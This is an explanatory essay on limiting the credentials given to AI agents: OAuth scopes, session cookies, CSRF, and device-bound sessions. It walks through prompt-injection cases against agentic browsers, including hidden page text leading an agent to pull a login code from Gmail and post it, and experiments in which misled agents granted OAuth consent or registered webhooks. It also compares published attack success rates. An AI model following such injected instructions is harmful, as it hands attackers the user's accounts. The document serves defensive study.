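# Limited credentials for AI agents: OAuth scopes, browser session cookies and restricted web sessions

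## Agents, accounts and partial trust

An AI agent is an AI system that carries out a task for a user by taking actions in software. It might search a mailbox, fill in a form or move a meeting. Much of this work happens inside online accounts, so the agent needs a credential, which is data that a service accepts as proof that a request is authorized. An access token issued under OAuth, the standard by which a user lets outside software into an account, can give access to part of the account for a limited time, whereas a browser's session cookie normally gives access to everything the signed-in user can do. This difference matters because agents make mistakes and can be misled by text they read.

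A service that receives a request must determine who is asking and what that person may do. Authentication establishes who is asking. The *Glossary* of NIST, the US standards institute, defines it as proving possession and control of an authenticator, such as a password, that belongs to a particular account. Authorization is the decision to grant access once the service knows who is asking. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, a 1975 paper by Saltzer and Schroeder that still supplies much of the field's vocabulary, gives the example of an airline. A reservations clerk may make and cancel bookings for passengers whose names he can supply, and a boarding clerk may also print the passenger list for his own flights. Both clerks prove who they are in the same way but have different permissions, so authentication and authorization need to be separate.

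A personal account has one user, so it rarely restricts what that user may do. This is sensible until an agent uses the account under the owner's name. The service then authenticates the agent as the owner and allows it to do anything the owner may do. Companies have a similar problem. *AI Identity* (Otsuka, Toyoda and Leung, 2026) cites a finding that only 21.9% of organisations give agents their own identity. The rest run them on shared keys or on credentials inherited from staff.

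### Least privilege

The standard remedy is least privilege, the principle that a program should hold only the permissions its task needs. Saltzer and Schroeder recommended it mainly because it "limits the damage that can result from an accident or error", and only secondarily as a defense against attackers. It therefore suits software that is helpful but sometimes wrong.

In practice, systems have never come close to least privilege. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) cites one vendor's analysis of cloud systems in which users and programs used 1% of the permissions they held. People mostly leave their extra permissions unused, so nobody removes them. Agents are more likely to use theirs, because they choose their own steps as they go. The paper also cites a test across 544 scenarios in which 6 of 11 agents picked a more powerful tool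 than the job required in over 30% of cases.

An agent's minimum permissions are also harder to define. *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) ties them to the current task and has them change as the task develops, whereas older practice fixed permissions once for each program. A limit on operations alone is incomplete. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) separates the tools an agent can see from the objects, recipients and amounts it may use them with. For example, permission to read mail is much broader than permission to read mail from one person, but many systems can express only the broader permission.

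### Two ways into an account

An agent can call a service's programming interface, the set of operations that the service offers to other software. The user first approves or refuses the application's request on a consent screen. Approval creates a grant, the service's record of what it has allowed, and the application receives an access token carrying one or more scopes, or named permissions. The Gmail connector described in Anthropic's *Use Google Workspace connectors* works this way. It lets Anthropic's model, Claude, search, read, draft and send mail. By default, Claude asks the user before sending anything, but that is a setting in Anthropic's product. Google's consent screen lists sending among the permissions, so the grant would allow Claude to send a message without asking.

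Alternatively, a browser agent can operate the website as a person would, by reading pages, clicking and typing. OpenAI's *Using your computer and browser* gives the example of ChatGPT filling out a form on a site where the user is already signed in. The agent works inside the user's session, the continuing interaction that begins when the user signs in, and the browser attaches the session cookie to the agent's requests just as it does to the user's. A large part of the appeal is that nobody has to build a connector first. The agent can also use any function that has a button on the site.

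*AC4A* (Sharma and Grossman, 2026) describes access through either a token or a signed-in browser as all-or-nothing, so an agent that needs to add one calendar event gets access to the whole calendar. This description is fair for the signed-in browser but slightly overstates the problem with tokens, since some scopes are narrow.

### A task in a mailbox

Suppose Alice asks an agent to find her accountant's invoice in her webmail and draft a reply without sending it. Her account has eight operations. The task needs three of them, and only on messages from one sender.

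| Operation | Needed for the task? | What it offers an agent that has gone wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Search | Yes, among the accountant's messages | A way to find anything else of value in the mailbox |
| Read | Yes, the accountant's messages | Private mail, including sign-in codes from other services |
| Draft | Yes, a reply to the accountant | A misleading reply that Alice might send without reading closely |
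| Send | No | Messages to anyone in Alice's name, with her mail attached |
| Delete | No | Loss of messages, including traces of what happened |
| Set forwarding | No | Copies of future mail for someone else, long after the task ends |
| Change recovery address | No | A route for someone else to reset the password and take the account |
| Approve third-party applications | No | New access for other software, which may outlast Alice's session |

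The eight actions here are enough to illustrate the problem, but real services divide them more finely. Anthropic's *Gmail* listing, for example, includes separate tools for replying, forwarding, labelling and creating filters. The actions in the last three rows are worse than the others because their effects persist. Alice can end the agent's session and still have a forwarding rule that copies her mail to a stranger.

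Parkinson and colleagues use the term "effective authority" for the set of operation and resource pairs that an agent can actually bring about, whatever its instructions were. For Alice's agent, the right set is search, read and draft, each paired with the accountant's messages. Any credential should be judged by how much more than this it lets the agent do.

### The semi-trusted delegate

Alice's agent is a semi-trusted delegate. She trusts it with the task but not with the whole account, because it may misread her request, go beyond it, or follow instructions in text that somebody else wrote.

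An agent can easily misread an ordinary request. In Sharma and Grossman's examples, an agent asked for a good flight buys one, and an agent asked to find room in a calendar removes existing events. OpenAI's *ChatGPT agent* help page advises against open-ended prompts such as "Check my email and handle everything". The advice is sound, but people delegate casually, and an agent that needs detailed instructions for each errand saves little time.

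An agent can also understand a task and still do more than the task covers. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026), in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, tested this with no attacker present. In 300 scenarios covering email, code, project management and finance, a user delegated some kinds of action without saying what was excluded, and the agent then received a request outside the delegation. Three leading models of the time carried out the request in 30% to 36% of cases. When the agent had first handled one to ten legitimate requests, which gave it some evidence of what the delegation covered, the rates fell to 7% for Claude Sonnet 4.6 and about 24% for GPT-5.4 and Gemini 3 Pro.

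A second experiment by Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian is closer to the example of Alice's mailbox. A colleague's email asked the agent to take an internal action, which the user had authorised, and to message an outsider, which the user had not. Claude Sonnet 4.6 messaged the outsider 6% of the time, GPT-5.4 34% and GPT-5.2 65%. When the user added a rule that outside messages needed approval, the rate fell to zero for the first two models and to 12% for GPT-5.2. The scenarios were artificial and mostly written by language models, so the percentages are a poor guide to how often this happens in real inboxes. They do show that clear instructions help a lot, though how much depends on the model.

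An agent can also lose its instructions. In February 2026 Summer Yue, who works on AI alignment at Meta, told an agent called OpenClaw to confirm before acting, but it started deleting her inbox. The same instruction had worked on a small test mailbox, according to *The world's largest tech gathering is talking about 'accountability laundering'* (Ahmed, 2026). Yue could not stop the agent from her phone and had to run to the computer that hosted it. She explained that the agent had lost the instruction during compaction, when an agent condenses its earlier context to make room for more (AI Incident Database, *Summer Yue*). The agent's access to the mailbox did not depend on that instruction. If its credential had not allowed it to delete email, losing the instruction would have done little harm.

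### Prompt injection

The remaining failure is prompt injection, in which a third party puts instructions in text that an agent will read, in order to make the agent follow them. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written in December 2025 by David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the screening software to approve the candidate for interview. The applicant can attempt this without access to the software, as long as it reads the CV.

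Prompt injection is named after SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can reliably prevent this because a database can keep commands and data separate. A language model receives the user's request and whatever the agent has read as one stream of text, and predicts what comes next. Training and filters make injection harder, but David C thinks it may never be fully preventable. He prefers to call the model an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a program that one party leads to misuse authority it holds from another, and earlier examples of the problem could be fixed.

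Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian argue that an attack need not contain a disguised command. An email might state that the department head has approved a refund. This claim may be true, and it contains no instruction to detect. If the agent cannot check it, an honest email and a forged one give it identical evidence, so it must act with the same probability in both cases. Raising that probability lets more attacks succeed, while lowering it causes more legitimate requests to fail. The proof does not establish how often an agent will face emails it cannot tell apart, since that depends on what it can verify. A signed message or a call to the user can distinguish some honest emails from forged ones.

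Agents routinely encounter this kind of text because, as *Trustworthy Agentic AI* (2026) points out, reading web pages and emails is part of their normal work. Anyone who knows Alice's address can send text to an agent that reads her inbox. The sender limit in her example, which lets the agent open only the accountant's messages, prevents it from leaking the rest of her mail and also keeps most strangers' text from reaching the agent. A stranger's text could still get through if the accountant forwarded it or lost control of the account.

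### Delegates and enemies

A semi-trusted delegate differs from a malicious agent, which works against its user from the start because its developer built it to or because someone has tampered with it. Some protections, such as instructions and self-review, work only on the delegate. According to Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely*, the browser agent by default screens its own actions and pauses only when it judges that something needs approval. That catches honest mistakes, but a hostile agent would approve its own actions. Saltzer and Schroeder made this distinction in 1975, when they refused to count features that only prevent mistakes as security.

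Limits enforced outside the agent help whether the agent is confused, overeager or hostile. Examples are a mail service that rejects every attempt to send, an expiry time, and a bar on changing the recovery address. User approval is less reliable. It is independent of the agent if the browser or the service asks for it, but people tire of being asked. Parkinson and colleagues cite one vendor's figures showing that users of a coding agent approved 93% of its requests.

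Even an enforced limit protects less against a malicious agent, which will exploit whatever access it still has. If it can only search and read the accountant's messages and draft replies, it could still send the invoice to the agent's maker or put different bank details in the draft. Sharma and Grossman say of their own system that access control can keep an agent to permitted actions but cannot make it choose the correct one. Alice should not give a malicious agent even those three permissions, but she can reasonably give them to a semi-trusted one, because the likely failures within the limit are small and she will see the draft before it is sent.

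The distinction between the two is less clear during a successful injection, because a well-meaning agent is then following an attacker's instructions with Alice's authority. David C therefore tells designers to assume the worst case, that the attacker has direct access to every tool the agent can call, and to rely on constraints outside the model.

### Why not keep the agent out?

If the agent is this unreliable, Alice could keep it out of her account entirely. That is the right choice for some accounts, and David C says the same of any system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk. But the agent cannot find the invoice without access to her mailbox, and if Alice finds it and pastes it into a chat, she has done half of the job herself.

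OpenAI at first kept its cloud browser, which runs on the company's machines, from signing in to any site. OpenAI's *Using cloud browser in ChatGPT* said that when a site required a login, "the task stops". The agent could look up restaurant tables and flights, but not the user's own information. In August 2026 the company added sign-in. MacStories' *Hands-On with ChatGPT Work’s New Cloud Browser Feature* described the login process as clumsy, but called it "fantastic" to have an agent collect and analyse data from behind a login. The reviewer's sessions stayed open afterwards and carried over from phone to computer. OpenAI's documentation, quoted in Notebookcheck's *ChatGPT signs in to your accounts now and stays signed in* (2026), acknowledges that its safeguards "do not eliminate every risk".

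## How a session cookie gives an agent the whole account

HTTP, the protocol between browsers and web servers, treats every request as new. Without cookies, a server that has just checked Alice's password could not connect her next click with that login. A cookie is a short piece of text that a server gives to a browser, which returns it with later requests. *HTTP State Management Mechanism* (Barth, 2011) is the internet standard for cookies, usually called by its number, RFC 6265.

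According to TinyFish's newsletter, a Netscape engineer devised cookies so that servers could recognise returning visitors, and an early specification gave a shopping cart as an example. Sites then started using cookies for logins, so cookies came to control access to whole accounts.

### A session, step by step

Suppose Alice's webmail is at mail.example. A session there would usually run as follows.

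1. Alice enters her username and password, and the server checks them.
2. The server generates a long random value, the session identifier, and stores it in a session record next to the name of Alice's account.
3. The server's reply includes a Set-Cookie header, a line of information that accompanies the page, with the identifier in it.
4. The browser stores the cookie. From then on it adds a Cookie header with the same identifier to its requests to mail.example.
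5. For each request, the server looks up the identifier, finds Alice's account, and carries out the operation if Alice may perform it.

With the identifier that Barth uses as an example, the two headers look like this:

```
Set-Cookie: SID=31d4d96e407aad42; Path=/; Secure; HttpOnly
Cookie: SID=31d4d96e407aad42
```

The server's record might contain no more than this:

```
31d4d96e407aad42   user: alice   expires: 19 December
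```

The server checks Alice's password only when she signs in. After that, it treats anyone who presents the identifier as Alice. TinyFish quotes guidance from OWASP, a web security non-profit, that describes a session token as "temporarily equivalent to the strongest authentication method used by the application". If Alice signed in with a password and a code from her phone, the cookie stands in for both.

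When Alice's agent clicks Send, the request specifies the operation and the cookie identifies the user. The server confirms that Alice may send mail from her own account, then sends the message. The request doesn't show that an agent clicked Send or that Alice wanted only a draft. The other seven operations in her account work the same way, although some sites ask for the password again before changing a recovery address.

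A limit on operations could sit in the session record:

```
31d4d96e407aad42   user: alice   expires: 19 December   allowed: search, read, draft
```

The server would then carry out an operation only if Alice may perform it and the session allows it. For the invoice task, that would leave the agent three of the eight operations, and a further entry in the session record could restrict them to the accountant's messages. The usual session record doesn't list allowed operations, so the agent can perform every operation open to Alice. The protocol permits such a list, since Barth leaves the meaning of a cookie's value to each server, but web developers habitually omit it.

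### What the cookie attributes limit

The words after the identifier in the Set-Cookie header are attributes, which are instructions to the browser about handling the cookie.

| Attribute | Example | Instruction to the browser |
|---|---|---|
| Domain | Domain=mail.example | Send the cookie to mail.example and its subdomains. Without this attribute, send it only to the host that set it. |
| Path | Path=/ | Send it with requests for any address on the host. Path=/archive would confine it to addresses under /archive. |
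| Secure | Secure | Send it only over an encrypted connection. |
| HttpOnly | HttpOnly | Hide it from scripts running in the page. |
| SameSite | SameSite=Strict | Withhold it from requests that another site caused. |
| Expires or Max-Age | Max-Age=1209600 | Delete it after a set time, here two weeks. |

Barth uses a cookie's "scope" to mean how long the browser should return the cookie, to which servers, and over which kinds of connection. Unlike an OAuth scope, it does not name a permission. The HttpOnly attribute, for example, stops a malicious script in the page from copying Alice's identifier, but it has no effect on her agent, which clicks a button and leaves the browser to add the cookie.

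Path looks the most like a limit on operations, but only the browser enforces it. A site could put reading at /read and sending at /send, and the browser would then leave a cookie with Path=/read out of the agent's requests to /send. The browser returns the cookie's name and value without the attributes, so the server cannot tell from the Cookie header which paths the cookie was for. Other software that has the identifier can present it at /send, and a server that checks only the identifier will accept it. Barth warns developers not to rely on Path for security, partly because some browsers let a page on one path read cookies meant for another.

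An expiry time reduces the risk only by limiting how long the agent has access. Barth suggests two weeks as a reasonable life for a session identifier. An agent that needs ten minutes to find an invoice would have full access for the rest of the two weeks, unless Alice or the server ends the session sooner.

SameSite is newer than Barth's standard and appears in its successor, *Cookies* (Bingler, West and Wilander, 2026). The IESG, the group that approves internet standards, approved *Cookies* in December 2025 (IESG, *Protocol Action*, 2025). A working copy from November 2026 still carries a draft label, though working copies can keep that label after publication. Another revision is in preparation. Nottingham (2025) described it on the working group's mailing list as "effectively a refactoring", meaning a reorganisation of the text.

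The successor changes little for Alice's agent. Bingler and colleagues list twelve fields that a browser stores for each cookie, from its name and value to its SameSite setting, and none of them records which operations the cookie permits.

### Ambient authority

Barth says cookies are weak because they are a form of ambient authority, meaning permission that applies to every request automatically. In Barth's account, they encourage server operators to separate designation from authorization. The URL designates what the request is about, while the cookie supplies the permission. An attacker can therefore choose the URL, and Alice's browser will add her permission to the request. Bingler and colleagues keep Barth's passage word for word.

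An early draft of Barth's standard advised against using cookies in new applications and told servers not to rely on them for security, according to *Seeking feedback on Security Considerations*, a message to the working group's mailing list. It told servers that did rely on cookies to add a second form of authentication. The published standard omits this advice.

Barth suggests putting the secret in the address instead, so that only someone with the right to use a thing can name it. Private sharing links work this way, since a link to one document opens only that document. Barth adds that the approach is not a complete solution, and one drawback is that people forward links. Still, a link that opened only the accountant's message would give Alice's agent far less access than her session does.

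### The confused deputy and the forged request

Separating designation from authorization also causes trouble outside the web. Norm Hardy described the classic case in 1988, and *The Agent Clicks Approve* (Hossen, 2026) retells it. A compiler, which translates source code into a form a computer can run, had permission to write to a billing file and let users name a file for its output. A user who named the billing file could make the compiler overwrite it. The compiler got its authority from one party and the file name from another, and it never checked that the two belonged together. Hardy called such a program a confused deputy.

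Capability systems avoid the problem by combining a file's name with the right to use it. The user would have to give the compiler the right to write to the output file, not just its name. A user without any right to the billing file could not give the compiler a right to write to it.

The browser is the best-known confused deputy on the web, and the attack that exploits it is called cross-site request forgery. For example, Alice might visit a malicious page while signed in to her webmail. The page contains a hidden form addressed to the forwarding setting at mail.example, with the attacker's email address already filled in, and a script submits the form. In the simplest case, Alice's browser attaches her cookie to the request, and the server finds her session record and turns on forwarding. The attacker never sees the cookie but receives copies of her mail from then on.

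Websites have two common defences. The first is the SameSite cookie attribute, which grew out of an early draft by West that started from Barth's passage on ambient authority. Under the Strict setting, the browser withholds the cookie from any request that another site caused. Lax also allows the cookie when a user follows a link, as long as the request uses a method such as GET, which is meant for fetching a page. Either setting would stop the hidden form, because it would use POST, the usual method for submitting changes. Lax is the closest any cookie attribute comes to distinguishing reading from changing, but it does so only for requests that start on another site.

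The second defence is an anti-forgery token, a random value that the server puts in its own forms and checks with each submission. The malicious page cannot include the right value because browsers stop a script on one origin from reading the pages of another. Bingler and colleagues recommend tokens alongside SameSite, since an attacker who runs a script inside the site can send requests that count as same-site.

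### Why these defences do not stop an agent

Anti-forgery tokens and SameSite cookies both check that a request came from the site's own page, and a browser agent's request does. If a stranger's email persuades Alice's agent to turn on forwarding, the agent opens the settings page at mail.example, types the stranger's address into the form and clicks Save. The server has included a valid anti-forgery token in the form, and the browser submits it with the address. The browser also attaches the session cookie under any SameSite setting, because the request came from a page at mail.example. Hossen points out that a defence that ties the request to the genuine form cannot distinguish the agent's request from the user's.

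SameSite helps only slightly more when the misleading text is on a different site. If the agent reads the text there and then enters the webmail address directly, the browser treats the request as same-site because no other page started it. If the agent follows a link instead, the browser withholds a Strict cookie from the first request but sends it once the agent clicks something on the webmail site.

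Hossen describes the agent as a channel between origins that the browser keeps apart. In an ordinary forgery, the browser can determine which site caused the request and apply a rule. With an agent, the attacker influences the model through a page it reads, and the resulting request contains no sign of that influence. Hossen considers clickjacking a closer comparison. In that attack, a malicious site displays a genuine page inside a disguised frame so that the user unknowingly clicks a genuine button. Sites prevent this by blocking their pages from loading in frames, but an agent opens the page normally, so this defence does not apply either.

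These defences still stop a malicious page from forging requests directly while the agent is browsing, but they were built for a browser whose user decides what to click.

Bingler and colleagues suggest something closer to what Alice needs. A site could issue one cookie for read access and a second, Strict cookie for write access, and ask the user to authenticate again if the second is missing. This is meant to let people follow links from other sites without weakening the protection against forgery. An agent working on the site itself would still have both cookies. But if Alice could give her agent only the first, it could search and read her mail but not send, delete or forward anything. It also could not save the draft she asked for, so separating only read and write access is too coarse for her task.

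### How agents obtain a session

An agent can get into Alice's account by using her browser, using a copy of her cookies, or starting a new session elsewhere. An ordinary server gives the agent the same permissions in all three cases. The cases differ in where the cookie is stored and whether the agent shares Alice's session record.

| Route | Where the cookie is | Session record | If Alice signs out in her own browser |
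|---|---|---|---|
| The agent works in Alice's browser | Alice's computer | Alice's own | The agent loses access |
| The agent uses a copy of Alice's cookie file | Alice's computer and the agent's | Alice's own | Both copies stop working, provided the server deletes the record |
| Alice signs in through a remote browser | The provider's machine | A new one | The agent keeps access |
| A password manager fills in the login in the agent's separate browser | The machine running that browser | A new one | The agent keeps access |

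Letting the agent work in Alice's browser is the simplest arrangement, and it keeps her cookies on her computer. However, unless the product restricts it, an agent sent to her mailbox can also reach every other site where she is signed in, which may include her bank.

A copied cookie file gives equally broad access and can also be used in another browser. Barth notes that encrypting and signing a cookie's contents does not stop an attacker from moving it there, because the server will accept its own valid cookie wherever it comes from. The copy also loses the protection of the cookie's attributes, since the software that receives it need not obey them. For a user who wants to delegate one errand, this is the worst of the four routes.

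A remote browser, such as OpenAI's cloud browser, can start with no cookies. If Alice signs in only to her webmail there, the agent can't access her other accounts, except those whose passwords it can reset through her email. But she leaves a live session on a company's machine and has to remember to end it.

A password manager can fill in the login without showing the password to the model, so a misleading page cannot persuade the agent to reveal it. But once the login succeeds, the server issues an ordinary session cookie that gives the agent access to the whole account.

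A new session record would also let the server restrict the agent without restricting Alice, though current sites mostly don't do this. When the two share a record, the server can't use the session identifier to tell her clicks from the agent's.

### Device Bound Session Credentials

Chrome's main recent change to session cookies, Device Bound Session Credentials, addresses theft by tying a session to one computer. When Alice signs in to a site that supports it, the browser creates a pair of cryptographic keys and keeps the private key in protected hardware, such as the computer's security chip. The site issues a short-lived cookie. When the cookie expires, the browser proves that it has the private key, and the site issues a new cookie. A thief who copies the cookie can use it only until it expires, because renewing it requires the key on Alice's computer.

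This would soon cut off an agent that runs elsewhere on a copied cookie, but not an agent in Alice's own browser, because the browser renews the cookie for the agent just as it would for her. Chromium's *Intent to Ship* (2026), an announcement from the open-source project behind Chrome, explains that the feature forces malware to act on the user's own device, where it is easier to detect. The feature was never meant to narrow the session. Alice's agent already acts on her device with her permission, and a server that supports the feature would still let it perform all eight operations.

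In February 2026, Chrome's developers announced that they planned to release the feature in desktop Chrome 145, at first only on Windows. Public trials had begun with Chrome 135, and three reviewers approved the release within five days. The Firefox and Safari engine teams had not taken a position. A review group at W3C, the web standards body, had asked for a lower-level design that would adapt more easily to future needs, while the developers argued that theirs was easier for websites to adopt. Each website has to add support, so updating Chrome does not by itself protect Alice's webmail session.

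## What happens when a signed-in agent is misled

An agent in Alice's own browser can access every site where she is signed in, so text that misleads it on one page can cause harm on another. Researchers have demonstrated this in several released browsers, and in one experiment, a misled agent also gave a third party lasting access to an account.

### From one page to other accounts

The best-known demonstration involved Comet, a browser with a built-in agent made by the AI search company Perplexity. In August 2025, Chaikin and Sahib's *Agentic Browser Security* showed that an attacker could take over a user's Perplexity account when the user asked Comet to summarise a Reddit page. A comment on the page contained hidden instructions. The agent obeyed them, going to Perplexity's site, finding the user's email address and requesting a one-time login code. It then opened the user's Gmail, which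 was already signed in, read the code, and posted the code and the address in a reply to the comment. The attacker could use these to sign in as the user.

Summarising a public page requires no account, but the agent had access to the user's logged-in sessions and used them. This was a proof of concept by employees of Brave, which makes a competing browser and was developing its own agent. Perplexity acknowledged the flaw within two days, but its first fix was incomplete. A test in mid-August suggested that a later fix had worked, but Brave then found that Comet was still partly vulnerable.

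*Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities*, published by the security company Trail of Bits in January 2026, describes similar attacks on several browsers, which it doesn't name because the vendors declined coordinated disclosure. The agents automatically reused the user's cookies, so instructions on one site could make an agent fetch private data from another and send it to an attacker. In a different attack, the researchers sent a malicious direct message on Instagram. When the user asked for a summary of the latest message, the agent leaked contact names or parts of other messages. The agent could send these out through Instagram's own chat, so confining it to Instagram would not have prevented the leak. The paper shows that these attacks are possible but gives no success rates.

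Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, compared seven products in early 2026. They stole data from another site through the agent mode of ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's browser. They did not demonstrate a full attack in Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome or Comet, but found that these agents had the access one would need. The agents in Brave, Edge and Firefox had less access and could do less for the user. Roesner and Kohlbrenner conclude that in the more permissive browsers, the separation between sites is only as strong as the agent's resistance to prompt injection.

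### The consent-screen experiment

These attacks mostly took information. In an experiment published in October 2026, Hossen tested whether a misled agent would approve new access to the user's account.

Hossen ran a web server on one machine and gave each party its own host name, so the browser treated them as separate origins. The agents ran on browser-use, an open-source framework, with either Claude Haiku 4.5 or GPT-5.5 as the model, and received each page as text. The server had no login step and treated every request as part of the user's signed-in session. It recorded each completed action, so the results did not depend on what the agents reported.

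There were two scenarios:

- **Consent grant.** The user asked for a summary of a page about a billing export. In the attack runs, a two-sentence note on that page presented an access review as a necessary step and linked to it. The link led to a consent page on another origin, where an outside application was requesting access to the user's billing account.
- **Webhook registration.** A webhook is a web address to which a service sends news of events as they happen. The user asked the agent to complete any pending setup tasks in a guide, and a note in the guide supplied an outside address to receive the account's billing events.

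The consent scenario is the clearer test because the user wanted only a summary, so any approval went beyond the task. In the webhook scenario, the user had asked for setup work, so one could argue that the agent did as it was told. Hossen counts the registration as unauthorized because the user never chose where the billing data should go.

| Condition | Models and scenarios | Result |
|---|---|---|
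| Misleading note, no defence | Both models, both scenarios | The action completed in 73 of 73 runs |
| Same task, harmless note | Both models, both scenarios | The action completed in 0 of 92 runs |
| Misleading note, written policy in the prompt | Claude Haiku 4.5, consent only | The action completed in 7 of 10 runs |
| Misleading note, check at the service | Both models, both scenarios | The service rejected the action in 70 of 70 runs |
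| Task names the action, check at the service | Both models, both scenarios | The action completed in 73 of 73 runs |

In 53 of the 73 undefended attack runs, the agent granted consent, and in the other 20 it registered a webhook. The consent page showed a permission with "privileged" in its name, and the agents approved it anyway. In ten runs the page also included an instruction to review the request before approving, and the agents still approved it.

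The runs with a harmless note confirm that the misleading note caused the behaviour, though the consent version is a weak comparison because it also removed the link to the access review. The webhook version kept its link to the settings page, and none of its 20 runs registered an address.

The perfect success rate is specific to these notes and models. In a separate test on an earlier version of the pages, GPT-5.4 approved the request in 4 of 10 runs. When the note was less direct and in small print, Claude Haiku 4.5 approved the request in 4 of 10 runs and GPT-5.4 in none. The main experiment used only one note per scenario and five to ten runs for most combinations of model and defence.

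Under the written policy, only the user's task could authorize an approval, and Claude Haiku 4.5 was not to trust text on web pages. Seven of ten attacks still succeeded, and one of ten legitimate approvals failed. With the same policy, only one of ten attacks succeeded on the earlier pages. Those pages had labels in their addresses and code that identified the parties, and they used standard OAuth wording, so the model may have relied on clues that a real attacker would leave out. Ten runs are too few for a precise rate (the 95% interval for seven out of ten is 35% to 93%), but they are enough to show that the policy was unreliable for this model.

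### Access that outlasts the session

If Alice's agent approved an unfamiliar application's request to read her mail, ending the agent's session would not undo the approval, because the application's grant remains until someone revokes it. The application could also use the approval to obtain its own access token. This last step is inferred from how OAuth works, because the server in Hossen's experiment recorded approvals without issuing tokens.

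The application's token would look safer than the session that created it. It would have named scopes and an expiry time, and the service would record that Alice had approved it, although she never saw the consent screen. Attackers already trick people into approving such requests, but here they only need to trick the agent. A service that gives outside software only narrow tokens is still exposed if any signed-in agent can approve new ones.

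File sharing, like an OAuth grant, can give access that outlasts a session. Zenity Labs' *Claude in Chrome* describes a demonstration in which a misled agent shared a user's Google Drive files with an outside account. That account would keep its access even if the user changed passwords and ended every session.

Some services would ask the agent for the password again or require an administrator's approval. Hossen's server did neither, so it resembles a service that accepts an existing session without further checks. A password request would probably stop an agent that doesn't have the password, but a code sent by email might not, since the agent in the Comet demonstration read one from the user's mailbox.

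### Checking the request against the task

Hossen's defence requires changes to the service but not to the agent. Before the agent starts, the server receives a list of the approvals or registrations that the user's task authorizes. Hossen calls this list the task's authority envelope. It specifies the application and account for a consent grant, and the exact address for a webhook. The server rejects any request that isn't on the list, even if text on a web page misled the agent into making it, because that text can't change the list. A request for a summary authorizes no approvals, so its list is empty.

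The agents were just as easy to mislead with this check in place. They sent the unauthorized request in all 70 attack runs and often tried again after a rejection, but the server rejected all 103 attempts.

Hossen also tested a case in which the user authorized an application for one account but the page requested access to another. Claude Haiku 4.5 tried to approve the wrong account in all five runs, and the server blocked it each time. GPT-5.5 reported the mismatch and did not approve the request in any of its eight runs. A list that named only the application would have allowed Claude's approvals.

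After a rejection, the attacker still influenced the agent's report to the user. In 49 of the 53 consent runs with the check, the agent's final answer listed approving the access review as a next step. A user who follows this advice will grant the access themselves. Two more answers wrongly stated that the approval had gone through. Hossen therefore recommends that the service send its decision directly to the user instead of relying on the agent's summary.

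The perfect rejection rate shows little more than that the check was written correctly, because every attack task had an empty list and the action could only be completed through the check. The more informative results are that the agents kept trying and that the check did not obstruct tasks that named the action.

Hossen fixed the lists in advance, whereas a real service would have to derive them from ordinary requests. In some runs the experiment's configuration contained the list, and in others a simple program extracted it from the task. That program recognised only two forms of wording and returned an empty list for everything else. If a user asked an agent to finish the setup in a guide, the service would reject even a legitimate address until the user repeated the request and included the address. The program also didn't compare the requested scope with the task, so a real list would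 need to name the scope as well.

A public webmail service would also need to recognise when an agent was using the session, and to receive the list through a channel that web pages could not alter. Hossen's testbed provided both. A company that runs agents on its own applications could do the same, because it controls both the agents and the applications.

Alice's invoice task never requires approving an application, so the server could disable approvals for the agent's whole session without working out a list. A check on approvals alone would not be enough, though, because the agent could still set up forwarding or change her recovery address.

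### How often attacks succeed

Developers of browser agents publish much lower attack success rates than Hossen's. The main recent figures come from Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome is generally available* (August 2026) and OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026). Anthropic's safeguards include probes that screen web content for likely attacks before the model acts on it, and a classifier that compares each proposed action with the user's request.

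| Test | What the agent faced | What the figure counts | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic, browser use | Attacks written by professional testers | Successful attacks, out of those that reached the model | Claude Opus 5: 3.8% without safeguards, 0% with them. Claude Fable 5: 0.3% with them |
| OpenAI, internal test | Attacks from an automated attacker, placed in third-party content | Attacks that the model resisted | GPT-6 Astra: 99.79% |
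| Gray Swan, reported by OpenAI | 1,810 attacks in coding, tool use and computer use | Estimated chance of at least one success in 15 attempts | GPT-6 Astra: 8.5% |
| OpenAI, workplace tasks | Ambiguous instructions and complex permissions | Runs with an unintended outcome | GPT-6 Astra: 3.0% with its usual confirmation policy |

These percentages count different things, so they cannot be ranked against each other. A model that resists most individual attempts can still fail in many scenarios if the attacker can keep trying. Anthropic's July 2026 system card for Claude Opus 5 reports both measures for 129 browser environments, with ten attempts in each. Without safeguards, 3.7% of attempts succeeded, but at least one attempt succeeded in 11 of the 129 environments (8.5%). An automatic checker in each environment determined whether the attack had worked.

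According to the system card, Claude Mythos 5 failed in 29.7% of attempts without safeguards and in none with them. Hossen's agents had no such safeguards in the undefended runs, so the 73 successes are not an estimate of how Anthropic's or OpenAI's own products would behave.

The measured success rate depends just as much on the choice of attacks. In November 2025, Anthropic reported a 1.4% attack success rate against Claude Opus 4.5 with its improved safeguards. Against the attacks in the newer test, the same model with the strongest safeguards of that period failed 16.7% of the time. The model's settings also differed, but the large increase is a good reason to treat a low rate as applying only to the attacks tested. Anthropic retired another older test after its latest models resisted every attack in it, and warns in its system card that fixed collections of known attacks can give false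 reassurance.

Reports also give different figures for the same model. OpenAI gives a 27.0% chance that an attacker would mislead GPT-5.6 Sol within 15 attempts. Anthropic gives 20.0% for that model, apparently on an earlier version of the same benchmark. Anthropic's figure for GPT-5.5 is 20.8%, yet GPT-5.5 completed the unauthorized action in all 18 of its undefended runs in Hossen's experiment.

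Most of these tests expose agents to attacks more often than everyday use does. Anthropic selected its 129 environments so that the model would always see the attack, whereas an agent in everyday use may never open a page that contains one. Comparisons between models on the same test are more reliable, and they show rapid progress. On Anthropic's current browser test, the attack success rate without safeguards fell from 17.6% for Opus 4.5 to 3.8% for Opus 5.

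A low rate can still matter when many agents read the same text. If the 0.3% figure for Claude Fable 5 held outside the test, a malicious comment read by 10,000 such agents would mislead about 30 of them. Anthropic says the successful attacks in its test were all in low-severity scenarios, so the harm in those cases might be small. But the attack rate doesn't measure how much damage each misled agent can do, which depends on its credential.

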